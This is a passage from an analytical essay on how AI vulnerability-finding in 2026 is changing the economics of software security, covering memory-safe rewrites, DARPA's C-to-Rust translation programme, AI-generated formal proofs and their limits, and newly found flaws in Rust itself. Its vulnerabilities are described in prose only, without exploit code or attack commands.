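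More money has arrived for open-source software. On 21 August Anthropic announced a $35 million fund in *Bringing the cybersecurity capabilities of Claude Mythos 5 to more defenders* (Anthropic, 2026). That is over six times what the Core Infrastructure Initiative raised after Heartbleed. But the money comes from a company that sells bug-finding, not from the companies that depend on the software, so it does not show that attacks have pushed those companies to pay. In July the White House set up a clearing house called Gold Eagle to coordinate finding and fixing flaws. Few software makers publish their security budgets, so outsiders cannot tell whether spending has risen or only shifted from other security work to patching.

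Examples of retired components are rarer. The best candidate is XSLT, an old language for turning data files into web pages. Firefox's XSLT code contained several of the serious flaws that Mozilla fixed, including the 20-year-old one. But Google had announced a plan to remove XSLT from Chrome for security reasons in late 2025, months before Mythos Preview. So AI bug-finding can only have strengthened a case for removal that browser makers already accepted.

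No large software maker appears to have adopted a new rule on programming languages since April because of flaws that AI found. Mozilla, which sponsored Rust's early development, mentions no new rewrite in its account of the April work. This is weak evidence after only eight months, since Android's team took about four years after Stagefright to adopt a new policy on languages. Still, the first reaction to a large number of flaws was the same as after every earlier shock.

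### Will the crisis pay for redesign?

David Weston, Microsoft's vice president for AI security, argued at Black Hat in August that companies should redesign their software. He said they had relied on serious flaws being rare and expensive to find, which is no longer the case, and that faster patching still leaves attackers a gap to exploit. Because AI makes engineers more productive, Weston wants companies to use the gain to adopt memory-safe languages and formal verification: "Let's invest that productivity in changing the physics" (SiliconANGLE's *Safer software construction counters AI-driven threats*, 2026).

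The best evidence for this view is the kind of flaws the models find. About 70% of the 95 public vulnerability records on Anthropic's dashboard describe memory-safety errors, the same share that Microsoft reported in 2019. Android has shown that switching to a memory-safe language removes most such errors from new code. Rust does not remove all of them, since at least two of the 95 were memory errors in Rust code, including one in Firecracker, Amazon's software for isolating virtual machines.

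There is less evidence that the crisis will fund the change. Weston was making a proposal, and Microsoft's own Windows is still mainly C and C++. A new language would also leave many flaws in place. *IBM and Red Hat Fix 400+ Security Vulnerabilities* (Gonzales, 2026) reports that the two companies found over 400 previously unknown flaws in widely used libraries written in Java, which is already memory-safe. The flaw that Anthropic highlighted in wolfSSL, an encryption library in billions of devices, came from faulty checking, not a memory error, and let an attacker forge a website's certificate.

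### Or an endless race?

Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod expect AI to speed up the old cycle of finding and patching bugs. They call current efforts "a continual Red Queen's race that can never be won", after the character in *Through the Looking-Glass* who has to keep running to stay in the same place. They argue that AI makes code cheaper to write, so companies will write more of it. They expect the extra code to contain extra flaws, because AI coding relies on the same loop of testing and debugging as human coding. They say AI bug-finding will catch some of these flaws, but that there is no reason to believe it will catch all of them, and that it helps attackers at least as much as defenders. They also expect people to lose the skill and knowledge they need when the AI fails.

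The race continues because vendors still bear little of the risk. Buyers can seldom choose a safer product, and organisations that have the choice often refuse to pay for it. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod think that eliminating memory-safety bugs would be a big step, but that other kinds of problem would soon replace them.

The 2026 record supports much of this. Unpatched open-source flaws accumulated faster than maintainers could fix them, PHP needed a second round of patches within a month, and one fix in radare2 often led to several more flaws. WeLiveSecurity reported 169 vulnerabilities in Microsoft's monthly release for April, 118 in May, 571 in June and 622 in July, although the June total included many from other companies' products.

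Finding and patching bugs may be worthwhile even if the race with attackers never ends, as long as defenders stay ahead. Schneier (2026), in *Claude Mythos Has Found 271 Zero-Days in Firefox*, quotes Mozilla's claim that defenders can now win "decisively" and agrees, provided they get patches to users quickly. Firefox updates itself on most computers, but PHP's operators mostly have to install patches themselves, and three-quarters of them had not done so after six days.

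### Or will the flaws run out?

Tony Anscombe of the security company ESET, writing for WeLiveSecurity, suggests that AI could eventually work through all old software, while developers use the same tools to remove bugs from new code before release. Bug discoveries would then peak and fall. Anscombe admits that this may be "misplaced optimism".

Duplicate findings offer some evidence that the supply of flaws is limited. Between September and November, the number of findings marked as duplicates in Anthropic's ledger rose from 2 to about 1,670, which VulnCheck attributes to other people having found the same flaws first. Ecologists use such overlap to estimate how many fish are in a lake. If two teams each find 1,000 flaws and 230 are the same, the total is about 1,000 × 1,000 ÷ 230, or roughly 4,300. If the supply were endless, the teams would hardly ever find the same flaw. But the sudden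 jump looks like Anthropic updating its labels in bulk, and similar models tend to find the same easy flaws, which makes the total look smaller than it is.

Firefox is the best place to look for a decline in newly found flaws. Mozilla said in May that it had not yet run out of flaws to find. eSecurity Planet's *Firefox 158 Patches 77 Flaws, Including Sandbox Escapes* (2026) and Security NEXT's *ブラウザ最新版「Firefox 159」が公開* (2026) together report 244 flaws in two October releases, including 108 high-severity ones in Firefox 159. That is fewer than April's 423 but still about ten times the monthly rate of 2025. This comparison is shaky because Mozilla used to group many internally found flaws under one identifier and now publishes a separate notice for each. Braun and Kerschbaumer (2026), in *Firefox Security & Privacy Newsletter 2026 Q3*, warn that such counts are not a reliable measure of security.

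Better models and methods also keep finding more bugs in software that has already been checked. An OpenAI tool found bugs in radare2 early in the year and pancake fixed them all, but Mythos still produced 372 reports. The Arizona State team tripled the number of bugs it found in the same kernel by improving its method.

The disagreement is largely about how quickly people find flaws and how much code they write. In the earlier example of a team writing C++, about 3,000 memory-safety flaws remained when the average flaw survived for 2.5 years. If AI cut that average to six months, about 1,160 would remain, nearly all of them in the newest code. But if AI also led the team to write 2.6 times as much code, the total would return to 3,000. Finding flaws faster after release cannot remove those that programmers have just added, but teams can keep them out of released code by checking it beforehand,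 as Mozilla plans to do and OpenSSL already does, or by using a language in which the flaws do not arise.

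## Falling costs of rewriting and proving code with AI

The AI models that find flaws in old code can also rewrite it, or prove that parts of it cannot fail in certain ways. In the adoption rule, AI bug-finding raises p, the chance of a serious attack, while cheaper rewriting and proof lower C, the cost of prevention. The fall in C may matter more, because engineers and managers who rejected safer methods usually cited cost.

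### Porting a video decoder mostly by hand

A 2024 port of a video decoder from C to Rust shows what such a rewrite cost before AI could do much of the work. *Porting C to Rust for a Fast and Safe AV1 Media Decoder* (Crane, 2024) describes how the company Immunant turned the C decoder dav1d into a Rust version called rav1d. Prossimo, a memory-safety project of the non-profit behind Let's Encrypt, commissioned the port. Memory-safety flaws in an AV1 decoder are dangerous because the format is complicated and browsers have to decode video files from strangers.

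dav1d had about 50,000 lines of C and 250,000 lines of assembly language. The team started with c2rust, a program that converts C to Rust mechanically. Its output works but is no safer, because it copies the C line by line, unchecked pointers included, into unsafe Rust. Three people then spent more than 20 person-months turning this into mostly safe Rust. They kept the assembly, which a fast decoder needs, so memory errors there remain possible.

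If a person-month costs $20,000, the port cost about $400,000, or $8 per line of C. The Rust version was about 5% slower, and in 2025 Prossimo offered $20,000 to anyone who could close the gap.

### Google's rewrite of giflib

In 2026 Google's security team used AI to rewrite giflib, a C library that reads and writes GIF images, in Rust. Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* attributes the rewrite to the risk of memory-safety vulnerabilities. InfoQ's *Google Rewrites Critical C Dependencies to Rust Using AI and Differential Fuzzing* (2026) reports that the Rust version was as fast as the C one, and that the AI's translations still needed human oversight.

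Other programs depend on a library like giflib, so the new version has to behave like the old one. Differential fuzzing tests this by running both versions on the same input and many altered copies of it, then comparing the results. Any difference may be a mistake in the translation.

Runtime Verification has published the steps for a similar rewrite of Linux kernel code that reads video format descriptions from USB cameras. The old code counted the formats, reserved memory for that many, and then wrote them in. A malicious device could describe a format that the code wrote but had not counted, so the last one was written outside the reserved memory. In early 2025, Google reported signs that attackers were using this flaw against Android phones.

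The engineers copied the C code out of the kernel unchanged, wrote stand-ins for the kernel code around it, and compiled it as a separate library. They kept the counting step because leaving it out would have removed the flaw they wanted to prevent. They then wrote the same code in safe Rust with the same interface and labelled every difference from the C so that a reviewer could check each one. Finally, they compared the two versions with a differential fuzzer.

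People still have to judge whether a difference between the original program and its translation is a mistake. Dan Wallach, who managed DARPA's translation programme, gave an example in a conference talk (Wallach, 2026). A short C program copies a password into an eight-byte buffer next to the variable that records whether the password was correct. A long enough wrong password overwrites that variable, and the program grants access. Google's Gemini model translated the program into Rust that accepts text of any length and still rejects the wrong password. A differential fuzzer would report that the two programs disagree about long passwords, but a person would have to recognise that the C version is wrong. Fuzzing also tests only some inputs, so it can miss a rare mistake in the translation.

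Neither Google's nor InfoQ's summary of the project mentions a product that uses the Rust giflib. For now, the project is a successful demonstration on a small library.

### A million lines in six days

In 2026, Jarred Sumner, the creator of Bun, and a colleague used AI to rewrite all of Bun in Rust. Bun runs JavaScript outside the browser and was written in Zig, a language that leaves memory management largely to the programmer. *The day AI wrote a million lines of Rust*, a developer's blog post, reports that the rewrite produced 1,009,257 lines in six days and that the new version was faster and smaller than the old one. At the pace of the rav1d team, a million lines would have taken more than 30 person-years.

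The Pragmatic Engineer's *What can we learn from Bun's rapid Rust rewrite with AI?* describes a long struggle with memory leaks and crashes, which motivated Sumner far more than attackers did. Many of the bugs came from using memory after releasing it, releasing it twice, or forgetting to release it. Rust's compiler rejects the first two mistakes in safe code, and Rust releases most memory automatically. Sumner called compiler errors "a better feedback loop than a style guide". In the adoption rule, these gains belong to b, the benefit unrelated to attacks.

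The same feedback helps AI models, which can read a compiler's error messages and try again without waiting for a person. Niko Matsakis, one of Rust's main designers, argues in *What agents mean for Rust (and vice versa)* (2026) that the language is a very good fit for AI programming agents. Matsakis has an obvious interest in that conclusion, but Bun's experience supports it.

Bun is a weaker test of cost than the six days suggest. Anthropic owns Bun, so the team could use as much AI as it wanted. The rewrite also kept the old architecture and data structures, which usually leaves a good deal of manual memory management in unsafe Rust. AI tools did much of the code review, but a browser maker would want to check a million new lines more carefully, and people read AI-written code no faster than human-written code.

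### DARPA's programme and the Great Refactor

DARPA, which paid for the seL4 helicopter, now funds research on translating C to Rust automatically. Six teams began work on its programme, Translating All C to Rust (TRACTOR), in June 2025. DARPA's *Translating All C to Rust* sets the goal of producing code with the quality and style of a skilled Rust programmer's, a standard c2rust's output does not meet. MIT's Lincoln Laboratory tests the tools and publishes the benchmarks.

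One of the programme's six teams, from the University of Wisconsin–Madison and three other universities, received $5 million (Barrett-Wilt, 2025, *Translating Legacy Code for a Safer Future*). If the other five received similar sums, the programme costs about $30 million.

The engineering firm Galois leads another team, and its *CRISP & CLEAR* explains why the firm combines AI with conventional code analysis. When models rewrite old code alone, they produce compiler errors, invent things that do not exist, and run out of room for large programs. A harder problem is that C programs often let many parts of the code change the same data, which Rust forbids, so a translator may have to reorganise the program rather than convert it function by function. Wallach judged that models "sometimes" translate code very well. TRACTOR has so far produced research tools and benchmarks, and no major product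 is known to run code translated by those tools.

*The Great Refactor*, published in August 2025 by the Institute for Progress, a Washington think tank, is a more ambitious plan. It proposes a dedicated organisation to translate widely used open-source libraries into Rust, starting with underfunded ones that have had severe flaws. Bradley and Sastry asked for $100 million to secure 100 million lines of code by 2030, or $1 a line, an eighth of the estimate for rav1d. Central funding would address the problem OpenSSL had before Heartbleed, when each company that used it waited for another to pay.

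No funder appears to have backed the plan at that scale. Its target price looked optimistic in 2025, but Bun's rewrite makes it look more reasonable, at least for producing the code. The plan would also cover old code, which Android's strategy of using Rust for new code leaves in place.

Even after a library is translated into Rust, someone has to maintain the new version, and thousands of projects have to switch to it. Apache and Nginx have still not made Rustls their default.

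### Proofs for 239 test programs

Proof can make old C code safer without replacing it. In October 2026 Anthropic and the verification company Theorem announced that Claude had proved security properties for 123 open-source libraries. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) argues that AI can now find and exploit bugs so easily that the standard defences are no longer enough. The threat of attacks was therefore one stated reason for the work.

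The team started from tests that already existed. Google's free OSS-Fuzz service tests open-source libraries with small programs, each of which passes random data to part of a library and watches for a crash. One such program might hand the data to an XML reader. The team turned each test into a mathematical statement of roughly this form:

for every input x smaller than 64 MB, the compiled test program, given x, exits normally.

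"Normally" means without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed check inside the program. Claude then wrote a proof of the statement, and the Rocq proof checker verified each step.

Claude did this for 239 test programs, about two for each library. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports a total of about 180 million lines of proof, with some 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions. In the process, Claude found and fixed hundreds of bugs that years of fuzzing had missed, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used XML reader.

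The work took a few weeks, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026). seL4's proof took 20 person-years, though it established far more. AI companies charge by the token, a unit of text a little shorter than a word. If a line of proof averages ten tokens and a million tokens cost $25, the finished proofs come to 1.8 billion tokens and roughly $45,000 in computing costs, or about $190 for each test program. The real cost was probably much higher, because the model also had to read the code and make failed attempts. But even a hundred times as much would be only about $19,000 per program.

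### What the proofs leave out

A proof that a program never crashes does not show that it does the right thing. A login library that never crashes could still let everyone in. The proofs cover only the parts of a library that the test programs reach. They also assume a single thread, a fixed amount of memory, no libraries loaded while the program runs, and hardware that behaves as its manual describes.

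The proofs apply to versions compiled for RISC-V, a processor design whose simple instruction set is easier to model. Most servers and PCs use x86 processors and most phones use Arm. The compiler produces different instructions for each, and some libraries include separate handwritten assembly, so the proofs do not cover the copies most people run. The immediate benefit to users comes from the bug fixes, which repair existing code.

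Other teams have worked on processors in common use. The security firm Zellic and its partner V12 published a proof covering a complete Linux program on an x86 processor. Leip (2026) believes it is the first of its kind (*Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*). In November Google DeepMind went further with proofs about the unmodified code of libsignal, the library behind the Signal messaging app, compiled for Arm's 64-bit processors.

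Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026) report in *AlphaProof Code* that their AI agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of proof for libsignal. The proofs cover secrecy as well as crashes. Two of the properties are forward secrecy, which means that a thief who steals a phone's current keys cannot read older messages, and post-compromise security, which means that a conversation can become private again after such a theft.

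The result still depends on about 26,000 lines whose correctness the proof checker does not verify. These lines describe the processor and define "secure", and people have to get them right. They make up only 0.4% of the total, but a mistake could still go unnoticed in that many lines.

Kleppmann points out that proofs suit AI unusually well, because the checker rejects any invalid proof a model makes up and the model can try again. The checker does not establish that the specification is right, however. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, discuss an Anthropic engineer who had Claude describe one of the company's programs in a formal language and got 16 sets of bug fixes from a few short prompts. They consider the bugs real and the method excellent for finding them, but say that such a run does not show the code is correct. As proofs get cheaper, they expect the difficult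 work to be deciding what to prove. They work for Runtime Verification, which sells that kind of expertise, but the limits of the RISC-V proofs support their view.

### How much protection Rust still gives

The same AI tools have found memory-safety flaws in Rust itself. In November 2026 Microsoft's FORGE Lab reported several in Rust's standard library, which nearly every Rust program uses. Bae (2026) explains in *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library* that some of them let a program written entirely in safe Rust cause a memory error, which the language is supposed to rule out. Much of the library is unsafe Rust behind a safe interface, and the flaws came from unsafe code that relied on unwarranted assumptions.

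| What the unsafe code trusted | How that might go wrong |
|---|---|
| That other code would not panic (stop because of an error) | A function moves an item out of a list and then calls code that panics, so the clean-up releases the item twice |
| That code supplied by the programmer was correct | A function reserves memory for the number of items it is told to expect, and more arrive |
| That the operating system was correct | The system reports writing more bytes than the buffer holds, and the program reads them all |

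Bae had searched for the first two patterns before. In 2021, Bae and colleagues ran a conventional scanner, Rudra, on the whole public collection of Rust packages and found 264 memory-safety bugs. AI has recently made it feasible to search for the third pattern.

A month later, Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) described an attempt to have Claude prove that safe Rust really is safe. Claude found dozens of counterexamples instead. Faisal's *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (2026) describes one, a five-line program in safe Rust that reads memory after releasing it. The compiler had accepted such programs for more than seven years.

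These discoveries are less alarming than they sound because an attacker on the internet can usually choose a program's input but not its code. To exploit the compiler bug, the attacker would need a program whose author happened to write the unusual code that triggers it. Bae also defends Rust's high standard. If any safe program can cause a memory error by calling a Rust library, programmers treat the library as faulty. In C, they would often blame the caller for ignoring the manual, so many of these bugs would not count as bugs.

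A scan of ordinary Rust packages found problems that attackers could reach more easily. In *rust-in-peace*, the security researcher Sergey Gordeychik, posting as Sergei G (2026), used AI agents in August to scan popular packages and some larger programs. Gordeychik confirmed 63 of the agents' findings by triggering the flaws in running code. Two were in Chromium's Rust code for reading images, and six were in OpenAI's programming tool Codex.

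Many findings were panics, inputs that made a program extremely slow, or ordinary logic errors. A panic can take a service offline, but it stops the program before an attacker can take control. A few findings were more serious, such as integers truncated to a smaller type before unsafe code used them, similar to the integer overflows in Android's Stagefright library.

Maintainers had resolved 33 of the 71 reports by early August, a much higher share than the 12% of Anthropic's reports to open-source projects known to be patched, though Gordeychik's list was far shorter. Fixes do not reach users straight away. Rust programs normally include a copy of every package they use, so a fix to a package three layers down has no effect until each project in between has updated and released its own version. Fixes to the standard library also reach a program only when its developers recompile it.

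Proof could reduce the risk in the unsafe code that remains. *Verifying the Rust Standard Library* describes an open campaign in which volunteers and companies prove that parts of the library cannot read outside their memory or use memory before storing anything in it. The tools recheck the proofs whenever the code changes. The campaign covers only some functions and kinds of error. The FORGE findings suggest which parts to verify next.

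### Cheaper prevention against cheaper repair

AI also makes repair and hardening cheaper, so cheaper rewriting does not by itself determine what a firm will do. The firm in the earlier example faces a 20% yearly chance of attack and is choosing between hardening, which prevents 40% of a $100 million loss, and a rewrite, which prevents 70%. If AI cut the cost of both by 80%, hardening would fall from $0.5 million to $0.1 million a year and the rewrite from $5 million to $1 million.

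| Firm's share of the loss | Option | Yearly net benefit before | Yearly net benefit after |
|---|---|---|---|
| 50% | Hardening | $3.5m | $3.9m |
| 50% | Rewrite | $2.0m | $6.0m |
| 10% | Hardening | $0.3m | $0.7m |
| 10% | Rewrite | −$3.6m | $0.4m |

The firm that bears half the loss now rewrites its product, because an equal percentage cut in the cost of both options saves more money on rewriting, the more expensive one. It would still switch if the cost of rewriting fell by only 40%. Cheaper rewriting does not replace liability, because the firm that bears a tenth of the loss still gains more from hardening. Rewriting would now bring it a small gain, but it would switch only if the yearly chance of attack rose above 30%.

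How much the cost falls will vary by product. Models have made writing code much cheaper, but not recertifying a medical device, persuading customers to install a new version, or finding people who understand the new code. Those costs may make up most of C for old industrial software, where losses also fall most heavily on outsiders.

### What people had adopted by late 2026

Most of this work shows what AI can do rather than what industry has taken up.

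| Project | What its makers produced | Evidence of use by late 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| rav1d | A complete video decoder | Publicly available, but slower than the C version |
| giflib in Rust | A library as fast as the original | No product named |
| Bun in Rust | A rewrite of the whole program | Bun's makers rewrote their own main product |
| TRACTOR | Translation tools and benchmarks | Research |
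| The Great Refactor | A funding proposal | None |
| Anthropic and Theorem's proofs | Proofs for 239 test programs | Fixes for the bugs found; the proofs cover RISC-V versions |
| AlphaProof Code | Proofs about libsignal | The code is in everyday use |

Bun is the strongest evidence of adoption, but its makers were backed by an AI company and had a reliability problem to solve. Anthropic and Google paid for much of the other recent work in the table. Both sell the models used in that work, so these projects do not show that ordinary software makers are willing to pay for prevention.

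Verified code was already reaching many users before these AI projects. In 2025 Python replaced its built-in hash functions, which compute digital fingerprints of data, with verified versions. That year Signal also began checking proofs about its newest encryption code each time its developers changed it. As with the verified routines in Chrome, users had to do nothing.

More software makers seem to want these tools. OpenNET reports that Canonical, which makes the Linux system Ubuntu, has started developing its own C-to-Rust translator. Galois' *You Can't Patch Your Way Out of This* argues that if AI can automate proofs, security may no longer depend on patching flaws before attackers exploit them. Galois sells verification, and its customers have long included the US military, which paid for it before AI made it cheaper.
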